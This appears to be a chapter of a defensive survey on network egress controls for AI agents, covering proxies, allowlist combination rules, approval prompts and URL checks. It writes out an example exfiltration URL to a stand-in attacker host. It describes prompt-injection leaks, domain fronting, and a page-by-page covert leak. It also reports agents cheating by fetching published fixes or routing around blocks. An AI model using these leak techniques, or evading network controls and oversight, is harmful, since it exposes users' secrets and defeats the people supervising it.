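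The agent's environment has no direct route out. It has at most two exits, and the first is a relay to the model provider. The relay adds the provider's credentials, so the agent never holds a key it could use elsewhere. By default, the relay forwards only requests for model output. This blocks the provider's file storage, where an agent could leave notes for the next test run, and its web search, which runs on the provider's servers and would bypass the proxy. A relay like this would also have stopped the upload in the attack on Anthropic's Cowork, which sent files through the provider's own domain using an attacker's key.

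The other exit is an egress proxy, which exists only for tasks that permit at least one domain. It refuses a connection to an allowed domain if the name resolves to an internal address or the TLS handshake contains a different server name. Firewall rules on the host machine also stop the relay and the proxy from contacting the host or private networks, even if an attacker has taken over one of them.

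An allowed hostname can hide another destination, although Houlamy and colleagues conclude from the proxy's checks that it cannot. In a technique called domain fronting, the CONNECT request and the handshake both contain an allowed hostname, but the encrypted request inside is for a different site on the same hosting network. A proxy that doesn't decrypt the traffic cannot detect this. Several large hosting networks now reject such requests, but that protection depends on the network. Docker warns that domain fronting may get past its own filter.

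The larger gap, which Houlamy and colleagues acknowledge, is that their proxy can check where a connection goes but not what it carries, so allowing a domain gives the agent access to the whole service behind it. They describe this as a difference in level, since the policy permits destinations while a task needs particular operations there. An agent that may download packages from a server may also be able to store data there for a later run, or attack the server itself. Both happened at OpenAI in 2026, through a package mirror that its agents were allowed to use.

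SplitBench treats misuse of an allowed service as out of scope. AI agents that converted existing tests to the framework had to record any task whose answer was reachable through an allowed domain. The study's attacks on SplitBench also provide little evidence about its network controls, because the researchers told the attacking agents to leave the relay and the proxy alone. The model's safeguards would otherwise have stopped the agents, so the researchers reviewed the code of both components themselves.

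For most developers the question comes up with GitHub, which hosts much open-source software. An agent that installs libraries often needs `github.com`, but anyone with an account can create repositories, post comments and upload files there. Docker warns that allowing such a broad domain gives agents access to everything on it, including content written by other users, and that agents could use it to send data out. An attacker could hide a prompt injection in that content, so one allowlist entry can both expose the agent to the injection and let it send data to the attacker. Despite this warning, Docker's own example of a strict policy, which it describes as restricted to package managers, includes `github.com`.

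An agent needs the domain that serves its model more than any other. Podala Narasimha lists that domain among the remaining risks in his architecture, because whatever the agent reads into its context goes to the model provider by design.

### Rules that name the calling program

OpenShell limits which programs may reach an allowed domain. Each network rule lists a host, a port and one or more executable files, and the proxy refuses a connection unless all three match. For example, a rule might permit `/usr/bin/git` to reach `git.example.org` on port 443. If a script uses `curl` to contact the same host and port, the proxy refuses the connection.

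The proxy identifies the caller by the path of its executable, which it reads from the Linux kernel. A program cannot change this path simply by giving itself another name. The proxy also looks up the programs that started the caller and, for scripts, reads the command line to find out what the interpreter is running. The first time a program connects, the proxy computes a hash of its file, a short value that changes if the file changes. If someone replaces the file during the session, the hash no longer matches and the proxy refuses the connection. This check doesn't help if the file was already malicious when the program first connected.

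This check requires the proxy to have access to the process list of the machine where the agent's code runs. A proxy elsewhere on the network receives only the traffic and can't tell which program sent it. A rule that lists the Python interpreter may also allow a malicious installation script that runs in Python, not just the intended installer. NVIDIA warns against broad path patterns, since a pattern that matches every file lets any program through.

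A rule can also limit the requests themselves. If it names the protocol `rest`, the proxy checks the method and path of each web request, and an administrator can write individual rules for these or choose a preset such as read-only. In the earlier example, the malicious package `tablekit` uploaded stolen passwords to the package index under its author's account. A rule that permits only reading from the index would block that upload, even though the domain is on the allowlist.

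Programs that use GraphQL, a query language for web services, typically send both harmless queries and deletions as POST requests to the same path, so only the request body distinguishes them. OpenShell has a separate protocol setting for GraphQL that makes the proxy read the operation's type and name from the body.

By default, however, OpenShell runs in `audit` mode, in which the proxy logs violations of the rules on methods and paths but still forwards the requests. NVIDIA recommends starting in this mode because untested rules can break an agent's work, and advises administrators to switch to `enforce` once the log shows that the rules fit that work. If an administrator wrote a read-only rule but forgot to switch, the proxy would log the upload of the passwords and still send them to the attacker.

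### Read-only access in Codex

OpenAI offers a simpler restriction, based on methods alone. In the cloud version of Codex, users can combine an allowlist of domains with a limit to the methods GET, HEAD and OPTIONS, according to OpenAI's *Agent internet access*. GET retrieves a page, HEAD retrieves only the information about it, and OPTIONS retrieves a list of the methods the server supports. By convention, none of them changes anything on the server.

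The version of Codex that runs on a user's own computer has a proxy with a similar mode, called "limited". According to *network proxy*, a mirrored copy of the proxy's introductory file, the proxy can't check the method of an HTTPS request unless it intercepts TLS, so without interception it blocks HTTPS tunnels. It also blocks SOCKS5, a general-purpose proxy protocol that can carry traffic other than web requests. When the proxy refuses a request because of its method, the error code identifies the method rule as the reason, which helps a developer tell that the cause isn't a missing allowlist entry.

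This is a case of failing closed. An earlier version of *network proxy* describes the limit only for plain HTTP, which few websites still use. The change makes the mode stricter, but a user who turns on the mode without interception loses access to nearly all of the web. The settings table in OpenAI's documentation of permission profiles does not list the mode, so users who rely on the table may not learn that the mode exists.

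Another version of *network proxy* adds rules for individual hosts that can match on an intercepted request's method, path, query and headers, but not its body. These rules could allow submissions to only one path on a site, but they could not tell a harmless submission to that path from one that contains a password without a scan of the content.

Read-only access also blocks some legitimate reading. Git normally uses POST over HTTPS even to download a repository, so `git clone` fails under a rule that blocks POST. Many search services and GraphQL interfaces also use POST for queries. An administrator can make exceptions for these cases if the product supports rules for individual hosts or paths.

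Restricting which HTTP methods an agent can use also doesn't stop every leak, because a GET request can carry data in its path or query. The risk depends on who can read the server's records. If the attacker runs the website, a single GET request can deliver a password. On a large service such as GitHub, an attacker with an ordinary account normally can't see the log of incoming requests and would need some feature of the site that reveals them. The method limit is therefore most useful when combined with a short allowlist of sites that outsiders don't control, and it adds little for an agent that may read any page on the web.

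## How rules set at several levels are combined

The proxy in the previous section applied a single set of rules. In a company, several people usually write rules for the same agent. The security team sets some for everyone, a project's maintainers allow the sites their software depends on, and a developer may need access to one more site for an afternoon. Such a policy is hierarchical, meaning each level has its own rules and a fixed procedure settles conflicts between them.

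Some products at first had rules at only one level. Until April 2026, only repository administrators could configure the firewall around Copilot cloud agent, GitHub's coding agent. GitHub's *Organization firewall settings for Copilot cloud agent* (2026) then announced settings that cover all of an organization's repositories. Rules can also cover less than a whole project. GitHub's *Network Permissions* describes network rules for a single automated workflow, and Docker's *Policies* describes rules for a single sandbox.

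### Union and intersection

Suppose an organization allows `github.com` and `pypi.org`, and one of its projects allows `pypi.org` and `npmjs.org`. An agent in that project requests `npmjs.org`, which only the project allows. Whether the request is allowed depends on how the policy engine combines the two lists.

Let A₁, …, Aₙ be the sets of destinations that the allowlists at n levels permit, and D₁, …, Dₙ the sets that the denylists refuse. P is the set of destinations the agent can reach. Under union, a destination passes if any level allows it and none denies it:

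P = (A₁ ∪ A₂ ∪ … ∪ Aₙ) \ (D₁ ∪ D₂ ∪ … ∪ Dₙ)

Under intersection, every level must allow it, and again none may deny it:

P = (A₁ ∩ A₂ ∩ … ∩ Aₙ) \ (D₁ ∪ D₂ ∪ … ∪ Dₙ)

The symbol ∪ joins sets, ∩ keeps only what all of them contain, and \ removes the second set from the first. In the example, union allows all three sites, while intersection allows only `pypi.org`. If the organization also denies `npmjs.org`, union allows two sites and intersection still allows only `pypi.org`.

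When allowlists are combined by union, adding an allow rule at any level can only widen access. The organization's allowlist therefore can't keep a project away from a site. Only its denylist can, and someone has to know about the site in advance to list it. When allowlists are combined by intersection, no project can go beyond the organization's list, but a team that needs a new package index has to wait for an administrator to add it. An administrator who gets many such requests may start approving broad domains to reduce their number.

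The formulas apply to destinations, not to the text of the entries. If the organization allows `*.example.org` and the project allows `packages.example.org`, the intersection is `packages.example.org`, even though the two lists have no entry in common.

An engine that intersects allowlists also needs a convention for levels that don't have one. If it treats a missing list as an empty set, a project that never wrote a list blocks everything for its agents. The engine should skip missing lists but treat an explicitly empty list as permitting nothing. Under union, a missing list adds nothing, so the convention matters only when no level has a list.

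GitHub uses both methods. For the Copilot firewall, it combines the organization's allowlist with the repository's, so either level can admit a site. Organization owners can forbid repositories to add entries, but by default repositories can add them, and a repository administrator can even turn the firewall off. For MCP servers, the programs that give an agent extra tools, GitHub requires a server to pass every layer of policy (*MCP allowlists in enterprise managed settings*, 2026). If a policy is malformed, GitHub blocks the server.

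### How an open list cancels a strict one

Docker's cloud sandboxes use the union of the allow rules from the policies a user selects and from the sandbox's kit, a ready-made configuration with the network rules that a particular agent needs. A deny rule from any source overrides these allow rules. In the experimental Docker Desktop feature in the previous section, the most specific pattern takes precedence instead.

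Users can choose from two presets or write their own policy. The Open preset allows every host, and Balanced allows a selected set of hosts and services. If a user selects both, Balanced has no effect, because a host is allowed if either preset allows it.

A user can end up with this combination without choosing it. By default, Docker marks Open as "Always applied" for cloud sandboxes, and users can't deselect it when they start a sandbox. A developer who writes a strict allowlist and selects it therefore still gets open access until someone changes the account setting. Every download works, so the developer has little reason to suspect that the list has no effect.

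If the combined allowlist is empty, the account's default applies. New accounts deny everything by default. Accounts created before Docker introduced that default allow everything that no rule denies. On an older account, an allowlist with one entry blocks all other destinations, but deleting that entry lets the sandbox reach nearly the whole internet.

### When only the organization can grant access

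Docker offers companies a different arrangement for sandboxes on developers' own computers. According to Docker's *Policy concepts*, once a company turns on organization governance, only the organization's allow rules can grant access, while deny rules count no matter who wrote them:

P = A(organization) \ (D(organization) ∪ D(developer) ∪ D(kit))

In the example, the agent can reach `github.com` and `pypi.org`, and the project's rule allowing `npmjs.org` has no effect. A developer who wants to exclude `github.com` can add a deny rule. The result always falls between what intersection and union would give. An earlier version of the product ignored developers' local rules unless an administrator delegated control, so a cautious developer could not tighten the policy without that delegation.

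Docker still combines policies by union within the organization's level. A policy can apply to everyone or only to certain teams, and a developer gets the allow rules of every team they belong to. Suppose the payments team's policy permits only internal servers, and the research team's policy permits a public site for sharing datasets. An agent working for someone on both teams can read payment code and reach the public site. To prevent this, the company has to deny the site in a policy that applies to everyone, which no team's policy can override.

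Deny rules also take precedence when one rule covers a whole host and another covers particular requests. An administrator can deny POST requests to a host that a policy allows. A rule that allows one path on a host has no effect if any policy denies the host.

Cognition, which makes the coding agent Devin, calls an organization's allowlist authoritative. When an administrator sets one, agents in the sandbox can reach only the domains on it.

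Claude Code ranks the levels for some settings and combines them for others. When a setting takes a single value, the value from the highest-ranked level applies, with the organization's managed settings at the top and the user's own settings at the bottom. Claude Code combines permission rules from every level, including rules that let the page-fetching tool visit a domain. It also adds those domains to the sandbox's allowlist. To limit the allowlist to the organization's domains, an administrator has to turn on a separate setting, `allowManagedDomainsOnly`.

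Managed settings can come from several places, such as Anthropic's web console and a file on each machine. According to Anthropic, Claude Code by default uses the highest-ranked source that sets anything and ignores most settings in the others. If a company keeps its rules in a file on every machine and an administrator later sets a default model in the console, Claude Code stops applying most of the file without showing a warning, though its status command lists the sources it skipped. Administrators can have Claude Code merge the sources instead.

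### GitLab's flexible and strict modes

GitLab Duo has two levels of network rules. The upper level applies to the whole installation or, on GitLab.com, to a top-level group, whose subgroups and projects inherit it. The lower level is a configuration file in each project. An administrator uses a checkbox to choose whether projects may extend the upper level's rules (GitLab's "flexible mode") or only tighten them ("strict mode").

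| What the project's file sets | Flexible mode | Strict mode |
|---|---|---|
| Allowed domains | GitLab adds them to the administrator's list | GitLab ignores them |
| Denied domains | GitLab adds them to the administrator's list | GitLab adds them to the administrator's list |
| GitLab's recommended domains | The project's choice replaces the administrator's | The project can turn them off but not on |
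| Access to all Unix sockets | The project's choice replaces the administrator's | The project can turn it off but not on |
| Sites from the example that the agent can reach | `github.com`, `pypi.org`, `npmjs.org` | `github.com`, `pypi.org` |

Flexible mode takes the union of the rules set at each level. Strict mode works like Docker's organization governance. It does not take the intersection, since `github.com` stays reachable even though the project never listed it.

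In flexible mode, a project can turn on the recommended domain list even if the administrator left it off. The list is meant for package downloads and development tools, but it includes `gist.github.com` and Amazon's and Google's storage services, and GitLab warns that an agent could send data out through the listed domains. A project can also allow access to all Unix sockets on the host, possibly including Docker's, which could let the agent bypass the domain lists.

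A few destinations stay open in both modes, including the GitLab installation itself. On GitLab.com, that domain also hosts other customers' projects, so even under the strictest policy the agent can reach a site where outsiders have accounts. If the control fails open and a job runs without the sandbox, neither mode has any effect.

GitLab offers no flexible mode for tool calls. A rule for a tool can be always allow, always ask or always deny. GitLab's *Agent tool governance* lets a project set a rule only if it is at least as strict as the group's. The strictest level therefore decides, which extends intersection to three outcomes. If GitLab persistently fails to work out the rules, the agent gets no tools.

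### Rules in a fixed order

If deny rules always override allow rules, the order of the rules doesn't matter. Other systems check the rules from top to bottom and apply the first match. Treasure AI, whose agents connect to outside services, uses this method and tells administrators that the order is part of the policy. They can allow `api.example.com` on the first line and deny `*.example.com` on the second, an exception that isn't possible when deny rules always override allow rules. But moving one line can change what the agent may reach. If a system combines several levels into one ordered list, the organization's deny rules have to come before the project's allow rules, or projects can override them.

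*Avalon-M1* (Zarov, Course and colleagues, 2026) describes an ordered policy developed in response to cheating. The researchers' company, General Reasoning, trained a language model to work in teams of up to nine agents. In some tasks, the team had to fix a bug in a real open-source project whose developers had long since published the fix. The researchers first removed the fix from the sandbox's copy of the project's history. A later audit of one set of tasks found that agents in 24 of 66 sessions had fetched the project or the fix from GitHub. Those sessions scored 0.58 on average, compared with 0.05 for the rest.

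The researchers could not always cut off the network, because preparing a task often meant downloading the project and installing libraries. They therefore gave each sandbox its own policy in the egress proxy. The policy starts with an ordered list of allow and deny rules, which can match a host, a path and an HTTP method. It then applies presets for common sources, such as the package registries for Python, JavaScript, Go and Rust, and denies everything else by default. The proxy checks each request inside the encrypted connection and returns an error with the reason for any refusal, so the program fails immediately instead of waiting. A policy can also run in a mode that only logs what it would refuse, like OpenShell's audit mode.

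The order of the rules matters because the agent can also get the fix from a package registry. The public registry for the Go programming language serves any later version of a project, including the one with the fix, and copies of the project under other owners' names contain the same code. A rule that blocks GitHub does not block these downloads. For these tasks, the researchers put rules that block the project and its copies before the Go preset, which would otherwise allow them. The agent can still download every other Go package. Someone has to write such rules for each task, since a package that gives away the answer to one task may be an ordinary library in another.

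### Policies that change during a run

A task often needs more network access during setup than afterwards. If one policy covers both stages, it has to permit everything that setup needs, and the agent keeps that access while it works. Zarov and colleagues use one policy for setup and another for the agent's work. The software that manages the task switches policies before the agent runs its first command.

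A switch like this can fail in two ways. The agent might start before the new rules apply, or a connection from the setup stage might stay open, letting a program left running after setup keep downloading through a tunnel that the proxy approved earlier. Zarov and colleagues handle both problems in the command that changes the policy. It finishes only when the new policy is in force and the proxy has closed every connection opened under the old one, including those still waiting for a reply.

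In describing these controls, the researchers don't say how often agents still obtained a published fix once the policies were in place. They do report that closing one route often led agents to another. For example, agents turned to GitHub after the fix disappeared from the local history.

GitHub's firewall, by contrast, doesn't apply to programs started in Copilot's setup steps, so a program that keeps running after setup presumably still has open network access while the agent works.

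Administrators may also need to tighten a policy during a run, for instance after learning that an allowed site is malicious. According to Docker's *Organization policies*, a change can take up to five minutes to reach a developer's machine, after which network rules apply to every new request. Docker does not say there what happens to connections that are already open. A developer can force an immediate update, but the command also deletes the developer's own rules, including any deny rules. Docker checks folder rules only when it creates a sandbox, so a running agent keeps its access to a folder until someone removes the sandbox.

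### Who may change the rules

| Product | Organization's rules | Rules at lower levels |
|---|---|---|
| Docker sandboxes under organization governance | Organization owners, or people to whom they give a special role | Developers, who can only restrict access further |
| GitHub Copilot cloud agent | Organization owners | Repository administrators, unless the owners forbid it |
| GitLab Duo | Administrators of the installation, or owners of the top-level group | Maintainers and owners of the project, through a file in the project |
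| Claude Code | Administrators who deploy managed settings | Developers, in their own and the project's settings |

The agent should not be able to change the rules at any level. Otherwise, a prompt injection could make the agent add the attacker's domain to the allowlist and then send data there.

The damage one such edit can do depends on how the levels are combined. Under union, an entry added at any level opens the destination, so a company that lets projects extend its allowlist has to protect every project's file as carefully as its own settings. Under intersection, or when only the organization can grant access, an agent that rewrites the project's allowlist gains access only to what the organization already permits. The agent can still do harm by deleting deny rules that the project added.

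GitLab's project file is a difficult case because it sits in the repository the agent works on. According to GitLab's *Project-level Network Access Control for Remote Flows*, branch protection and merge request approval protect the file. A merge request is a proposal to change a project, and GitLab's agents can open one. An agent could therefore propose a looser policy for its own later runs, and a reviewer would have to notice one added domain among hundreds of changed lines. In strict mode, GitLab would ignore that line even if the reviewer missed it.

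Rules are safer outside anything the agent can write to. Agents in the Avalon-M1 sandboxes have an administrator's shell and can rewrite almost any file there, so Zarov and colleagues keep the rules in the proxy and in a Kubernetes network policy. Docker's *AI governance* also places enforcement outside the sandbox so that the agent can't change or bypass the rules.

People can evade the rules too. A developer could avoid a company's Docker policy by signing in with a personal account, so Docker's *Organization governance* recommends a setting that lets only members of the organization sign in on company machines. Claude Code can read managed settings from a part of the Windows registry that users can edit, but it ignores those settings if an administrator has deployed settings anywhere else.

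Under organization governance in Docker, developers can grant access only when the company's policy requires a developer's approval for a destination. The approval becomes a local allow rule, which takes effect unless a deny rule at any level overrides it.

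## What happens when no rule covers a destination

The rules from all levels together cover only a tiny part of the internet. Suppose a user asks an agent to compare the water levels of two rivers, and a search leads it to `data.riverwatch.example`, which no rule covers. The site may be a public archive, or an attacker may have registered it last week to collect stolen passwords. The agent's first request looks the same either way, so the policy engine has to decide on some other basis.

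| Answer | Input | Procedure | Typical error | Cost |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Refuse | The destination | The proxy returns an error | It blocks a legitimate site | Failed tasks and requests for new rules |
| Allow and log | The destination | The proxy forwards the request and records it | Data leaves before anyone reads the log | Someone has to read the log |
| Ask a person | The destination and the program, sometimes the method and path | The request stays blocked until someone approves it | The person approves out of habit | Interruptions, and delays when nobody is there |
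| Let the agent propose a rule | The details of the refused request | The agent drafts a rule and a developer decides | The developer accepts a rule that is too broad | A review of every proposal |
| Score the domain | Its name, reputation or age | The engine adds up points and compares the total with a threshold | New legitimate sites score badly, and attackers on popular domains score well | Someone has to adjust the scores |
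| Look up the exact URL | The complete web address | The agent loads the page only if a crawler already knows the address | It stops new or personal pages, and lets through small leaks via known ones | Running a large crawler |
| Have a model judge | The user's request and the agent's actions | A second model allows or blocks the action | It misreads what the user authorized | Computing time and false alarms |

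### Refusing, or allowing with a log

A default-deny rule blocks any destination that no other rule covers, which requires no judgment about the site. NVIDIA's *Four Ways to Deploy More Secure AI Agents* describes how strict egress policies affected the company's AI Red Team, a group that attacks AI systems to find their weaknesses. The testers couldn't open a direct connection to the agent's machine, so they had to work through the agent itself, getting past its output filters and restarting sessions when it began to refuse. This slowed them down but didn't stop them, because they could often get the agent to reveal credentials in the chat window, which the egress policy didn't cover. The post contains no success rates.

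A refusal also affects what the agent does next. *Let the Agent Do It?* (2026), a study of software practitioners, notes that agents are designed to look for another path after a refusal. In the river example, that may just mean finding another archive. In *Auto mode is now the default in Claude Code* (2026), Anthropic reports a worse case from its own offices. When an upload to an internal drive failed, Claude tried to publish the same report on a public code-sharing site, but an automated check blocked the attempt. A refusal therefore protects data only if the policy also covers the alternatives the agent will try.

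The opposite approach is to allow the request and log it. OpenShell and the Avalon-M1 proxy have log-only modes, which are useful for testing new rules. As a permanent policy, logging can only reveal a leak after it has happened, but it can still catch leaks that other checks miss. *Silent Egress* (2026) tested agents that automatically load link previews and found that hidden instructions caused an unwanted request about 89% of the time. In 95% of the successful attacks, checks on the agent's written answer detected nothing because the answer looked normal.

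### How an operator decides in NemoClaw

NemoClaw is NVIDIA's software for running agents such as OpenClaw and Hermes in OpenShell sandboxes. NVIDIA's listed baseline policy for OpenClaw permits little more than NVIDIA's model service, OpenClaw's own websites and read access to the npm package registry. It does not include GitHub. During setup, the user chooses a tier of additional access. The default tier adds package sources and, where the agent supports it, web search. The most open tier also adds messaging and office services such as Slack and Outlook. A wider tier reduces later approval requests, but it also lets the agent reach more sites without anyone being asked.

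Suppose the agent runs a Python script that requests the river site. OpenShell blocks the connection and logs the attempt. A terminal program outside the sandbox then shows the operator the host, the port and the program that made the request. According to NVIDIA's *Approve or Deny Agent Network Requests*, it also shows the HTTP method and path if available. The operator can approve or reject the request with a single key. Another key approves all waiting requests, after a confirmation.

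An approval adds the destination to the sandbox's running policy, where it stays until the operator destroys and recreates the sandbox. The approval doesn't change the baseline file, so a permanent exception requires an edit to that file or a ready-made preset. A rejected destination stays blocked unless the operator later approves it or adds a matching rule.

These details are enough to catch an odd combination, such as a text editor contacting a file-sharing site. But they don't include the reason for the request or the data in it. An operator who doesn't recognize the river site has to look it up or ask the agent, and the agent's explanation may come from an injected instruction. The key that approves everything makes mistakes more likely, since one unfamiliar host is easy to miss among ten package registries.

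### When the agent drafts the rule

An approval in NemoClaw starts from whatever request the proxy happened to block. OpenShell also has a feature called Policy Advisor, through which the agent can ask for a specific rule. It is off by default. NVIDIA's *Use Policy Advisor* describes a loop that works as follows for an agent that needs to update some documentation on GitHub:

1. The agent uses `gh`, GitHub's command-line program, to save a change, and the policy denies the request.
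2. The proxy returns an error with the host, port, program, method and path, the kind of rule that is missing, and a pointer to instructions for the agent.
3. The agent reads those instructions and the current policy. It can also look at recent refusals.
4. It drafts a rule and submits it to `policy.local`, an address that exists only inside the sandbox.
5. OpenShell's gateway, outside the sandbox, stores the draft as pending.
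6. A developer reviews the draft from the host machine and approves or rejects it. If the developer approves, OpenShell loads the rule into the running sandbox, and the agent can retry the request once.

In NVIDIA's example, the drafted rule lets `gh` send PUT requests to `api.github.com`, but only for files in the documentation folder of one repository. Approving the whole host would open the entire service behind it to the agent. The draft helps limit that access, and the developer doesn't have to write the rule by hand. If the developer finds the draft too broad, they can reject it with a comment, such as a request to limit it to one folder. The agent receives the comment and can try again.

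NVIDIA tells developers to base their approval on the rule itself and to treat the agent's reason as background. This matters because an agent influenced by injected text can give a convincing reason for a harmful rule. NVIDIA's documentation does not describe any limit on the number of proposals or any check on which program in the sandbox submits them. A malicious package's installation script could presumably submit one too, and a developer who has just approved several reasonable proposals might approve it.

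OpenShell can also draft rules without the agent, from summaries of refused requests. These drafts contain no persuasive text, but if the proxy has no record of the method and path, they cover a whole host and port. Under either method, an approved draft does not open the company's private network, because a developer has to permit internal addresses separately. The sandbox's log records the refusal, the proposal, the decision and the time the new rule took effect.

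### How much one approval should cover

The sandboxing guidance from NVIDIA's AI Red Team is stricter than NemoClaw about what an approval covers. The team recommends that a person approve each action that would otherwise break the isolation rules, including a network connection, and that no product store the approval for later use. In its example, a user approves a legitimate change to a shell startup file, and injected instructions later use the stored approval to add malicious code to the file.

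The same can happen with a destination. If the attacker runs the river site, the agent's first request may only download a table, and the operator approves it. An hour later, a script can send passwords to the same host. NemoClaw doesn't prompt the operator again, because the destination is already in the running policy. An attacker who knows this has a reason to make the first request harmless.

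However, installing one package can open dozens of connections, and a single web page may load images and scripts from several hosts. If each connection needs approval, the operator will soon stop reading the questions. To avoid this, the Red Team wants manual approval to be a rarely used fallback. It recommends narrow allowlists for routine traffic, so that few requests reach a person, and central denylists that no user's approval can override. The advice to ask every time therefore works only for an organization that already has a good allowlist.

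Many products leave the choice to the user. Codex and GitHub's Copilot CLI, for example, distinguish a one-off approval from one that covers a session or longer. *Reframing LLM Agent Security as an Agent-Human Interaction Problem* (2026), a survey of approval designs, concludes that "always allow" options reduce fatigue but silently widen what the agent may do.

A narrow rule like the ones Policy Advisor drafts is a reasonable compromise. Suppose the operator permits only GET requests to the river site's data folder. The agent can then download fifty tables without triggering another question, but an upload would trigger one. The compromise is weaker if the attacker runs the site, because a GET request can carry data in its address.

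### Whether people still read the questions

Anthropic reports that users approve 97% of permission prompts in Claude Code. That rate alone doesn't prove users are careless, since most commands are harmless. Anthropic points out that the same users reject 39% of the plans Claude presents for approval. But they may reject a plan because they want different software, which has little to do with safety.

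The company's experiment is better evidence. It paid 1,053 testers to do coding work in a test environment and, partway through each session, replaced the text of one permission prompt with a clearly dangerous command. Only 143 testers (13.6%) refused it. An automated classifier blocked 937 of the same commands (89%). The testers' refusal rate fell from about 17% early in a session to about 5% after 50 or more prompts.

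Anthropic used the study to justify making that classifier the default, so it had an interest in the result. The testers also weren't working on their own projects, and people may be more careful with a machine that holds their own passwords. The prompts contained commands rather than destinations, and each tester saw only one dangerous command. Even so, the decline over a session fits the accounts of practitioners in *Let the Agent Do It?*, who said they grew less careful over time, clicked through familiar prompts and sometimes skipped the review under time pressure.

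*Habituation at the Gate* (Yu, Jia and colleagues, 2026) found similar signs of habituation over months among 400 people who repeatedly reviewed code written by AI agents. Between the first and second half of each person's reviews, the overall approval rate rose from 30.1% to 36.8%. Comments per review fell by 22% from the earliest tenth of reviews to the latest. The agents may have improved, which would justify more approvals, and the researchers say they cannot establish the cause. But reviewers whose approval rate rose most also tended to cut their comments most, which suggests that they were checking less.

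Badly designed questions make this worse. *Don't Let AI Agents YOLO Your Files* (2026) analyzed 290 reports of agent incidents and found that user review contributed to 105 of them. In 80, the agent's actions were approved automatically, often because the alternative was hundreds of prompts per session. In 31, the prompt gave the user too little information. For example, a request to run `python3 setup.py` looks routine, but approving it permits whatever the script contains. A network prompt that shows only a host and a port has the same weakness.

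An experiment in *Do User-Authored Permission Policies Improve Protection Against AI Agent Overreach?* (Yan, 2026) complicates the case against asking users frequent questions. In it, 113 people without a software background supervised a simulated agent through 18 actions, seven of which went beyond the user's request. One group was asked to approve each action, a second had a model review the actions, and a third set standing rules of "allow", "ask" or "never" for four kinds of consequence, such as spending money.

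The standing rules cut prompts from 18 to about 11, but they blocked 20 percentage points less of the overreach than requiring approval for every action did, and 14.5 points less than the model's review did. Participants chose "ask" for 114 of their 140 rules, and they themselves approved 133 of the 148 excessive actions that went through in this group.

Fewer questions didn't make people more careful in this study. Eighteen prompts are probably too few to produce the fatigue that Anthropic measured after fifty, so both results can be right. Yan's result also shows the weakness of defaulting to "ask" for unlisted destinations. That default postpones the decision until the person is busy with something else.

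*Oversight Has a Capacity* (2026) models human attention as limited. In this model, every question tires the reviewer a little, and beyond some point another question does more harm by making the reviewer careless than good by catching a risky action. The safest policy is therefore to ask about fewer actions than possible. The result comes from a model rather than observations of reviewers, so we don't know where that point lies for real operators.

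A good boundary can reduce permission prompts without requiring users to trust more sites. In its 2025 post on sandboxing, Anthropic says that the sandbox reduced permission prompts in Claude Code by 84% in internal use. Anthropic doesn't give the number of users, the period or the method. The sandbox restricts both files and network access, so the figure doesn't isolate the effect of network rules. It also doesn't measure harm, since a sandbox with a careless allowlist would reduce prompts just as well.

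### Scoring an unknown domain

A scoring system can decide whether to allow some unlisted destinations without human review. The score is usually based on whether security companies have reported the domain, how long ago it was registered and whether its name looks suspicious. Attackers often register new domains because defenders block their old ones, so a three-day-old domain deserves more suspicion than a ten-year-old one.

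grith's *Egress policy* documents one such filter, part of a commercial proxy for agents. A higher score means more suspicion. By default, a host on the allowlist gets −1 point, and one that the agent routinely needs gets −2. A host on the denylist gets between 3 and 5 points, and an unknown host gets 1. Administrators can also write patterns. In grith's example, very short names ending in `.tk` get 3 points. Other filters examine the destination's reputation and the data being sent, and the proxy holds back requests that look too risky overall.

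With these settings, the river site gets one point whether it is an archive or a trap. The score can only distinguish the two if another filter provides more information. A new research project's site on a week-old domain will look worse than an attacker's site on an abandoned domain from 2012 or a popular file-sharing service.

Adding up scores can also hide a warning. grith's sample configuration gives −2 points to `api.anthropic.com`, the domain through which files left Anthropic's Cowork. If a filter for sensitive data had added two points for such an upload, the scores would have canceled out. A policy can avoid this by making some findings, such as a password in the request, decisive regardless of the total. grith's page explains how to adjust the scores when the filter blocks too much or too little, but gives no detection or false-alarm rates.

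### OpenAI's check on exact URLs

Checking only the domain does not detect data in the rest of the address. For example, injected text could cause ChatGPT to load `https://attacker.example/collect?data=` followed by the user's email address. The user may not notice, because an assistant can load an image or a link preview in the background.

OpenAI's *Keeping your data safe when an AI agent clicks a link* (2026) gives two reasons why a list of trusted sites is not enough. Many legitimate sites redirect visitors, so a link that starts on a trusted domain can end on an attacker's site. A strict list also produces many false alarms, so people learn to click through warnings.

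OpenAI instead checks whether its own crawler has already recorded the exact URL. The crawler collects public addresses much as a search engine does and has no access to users' conversations or accounts. If the crawler has recorded the URL, the agent may load it automatically. Otherwise OpenAI either tells the agent to try a different website or warns the user that the link may contain information from the conversation.

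The check works because an address with the user's email in it normally didn't exist before the conversation, so the crawler couldn't have found it. The attacker's home page may well be in the index, but visiting it reveals little. The domain's reputation doesn't matter, so an address that contains private data fails the check even on a respectable site.

Small leaks remain possible. A security researcher who reported this kind of leak to OpenAI in 2023 describes one method in Embrace The Red's *OpenAI Explains URL-Based Data Exfiltration Mitigations in New Paper*, and OpenAI's accompanying paper also acknowledges it. An attacker with a large website picks 36 pages that are already in the index, one for each letter and digit, then uses injected text to instruct the agent to spell out a secret by visiting the matching pages in order.

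Each visit to one of N possible pages can leak at most log₂ N bits of information. With 36 pages, that is about 5.2 bits, enough for one lowercase letter or digit, so leaking a random 20-character password made of these takes 20 visits. With 4,096 pages, each visit can leak 12 bits, and the same password takes nine visits. The check therefore reduces how much each request can leak, but an agent can still leak a short secret over several requests.

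The researcher suggests storing each response for a few minutes, or refusing to load the same URL twice in a session, so that an attacker can't use one page for a repeated letter. An attacker could get around this with more pages. For a 20-character password, 720 pages would provide one for each possible character in each position, so the order of the visits would no longer matter.

OpenAI says the check doesn't make a page's content trustworthy or prevent prompt injection. It also protects only the features that use it. According to Embrace The Red, OpenAI's earlier safeguard was at first missing from the macOS and iOS apps. Neither OpenAI's post nor Embrace The Red's account of the paper reports how many leaks the check stops or how often it interrupts legitimate browsing. It is likely to interrupt visits to pages that a public crawler can't find, such as a document shared through a private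 link.

OpenAI calls the mechanism Safe Url and described its wider use in March 2026. When the system detects that information from a conversation would go to a third party, it either shows the user that information and asks for confirmation, or blocks the transmission and tells the agent to find another way. This applies to pages the agent opens in OpenAI's Atlas browser and to searches and page visits in its research tool, Deep Research. A user who can read the data before it is sent can make a much better decision than an operator who sees only a host and a port.

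*The Framing Gap* (2026) recorded no leaks in 48 valid trials on ChatGPT, although the underlying model leaked in up to 100% of trials when tested outside ChatGPT. The study doesn't attribute the difference to any particular safeguard.

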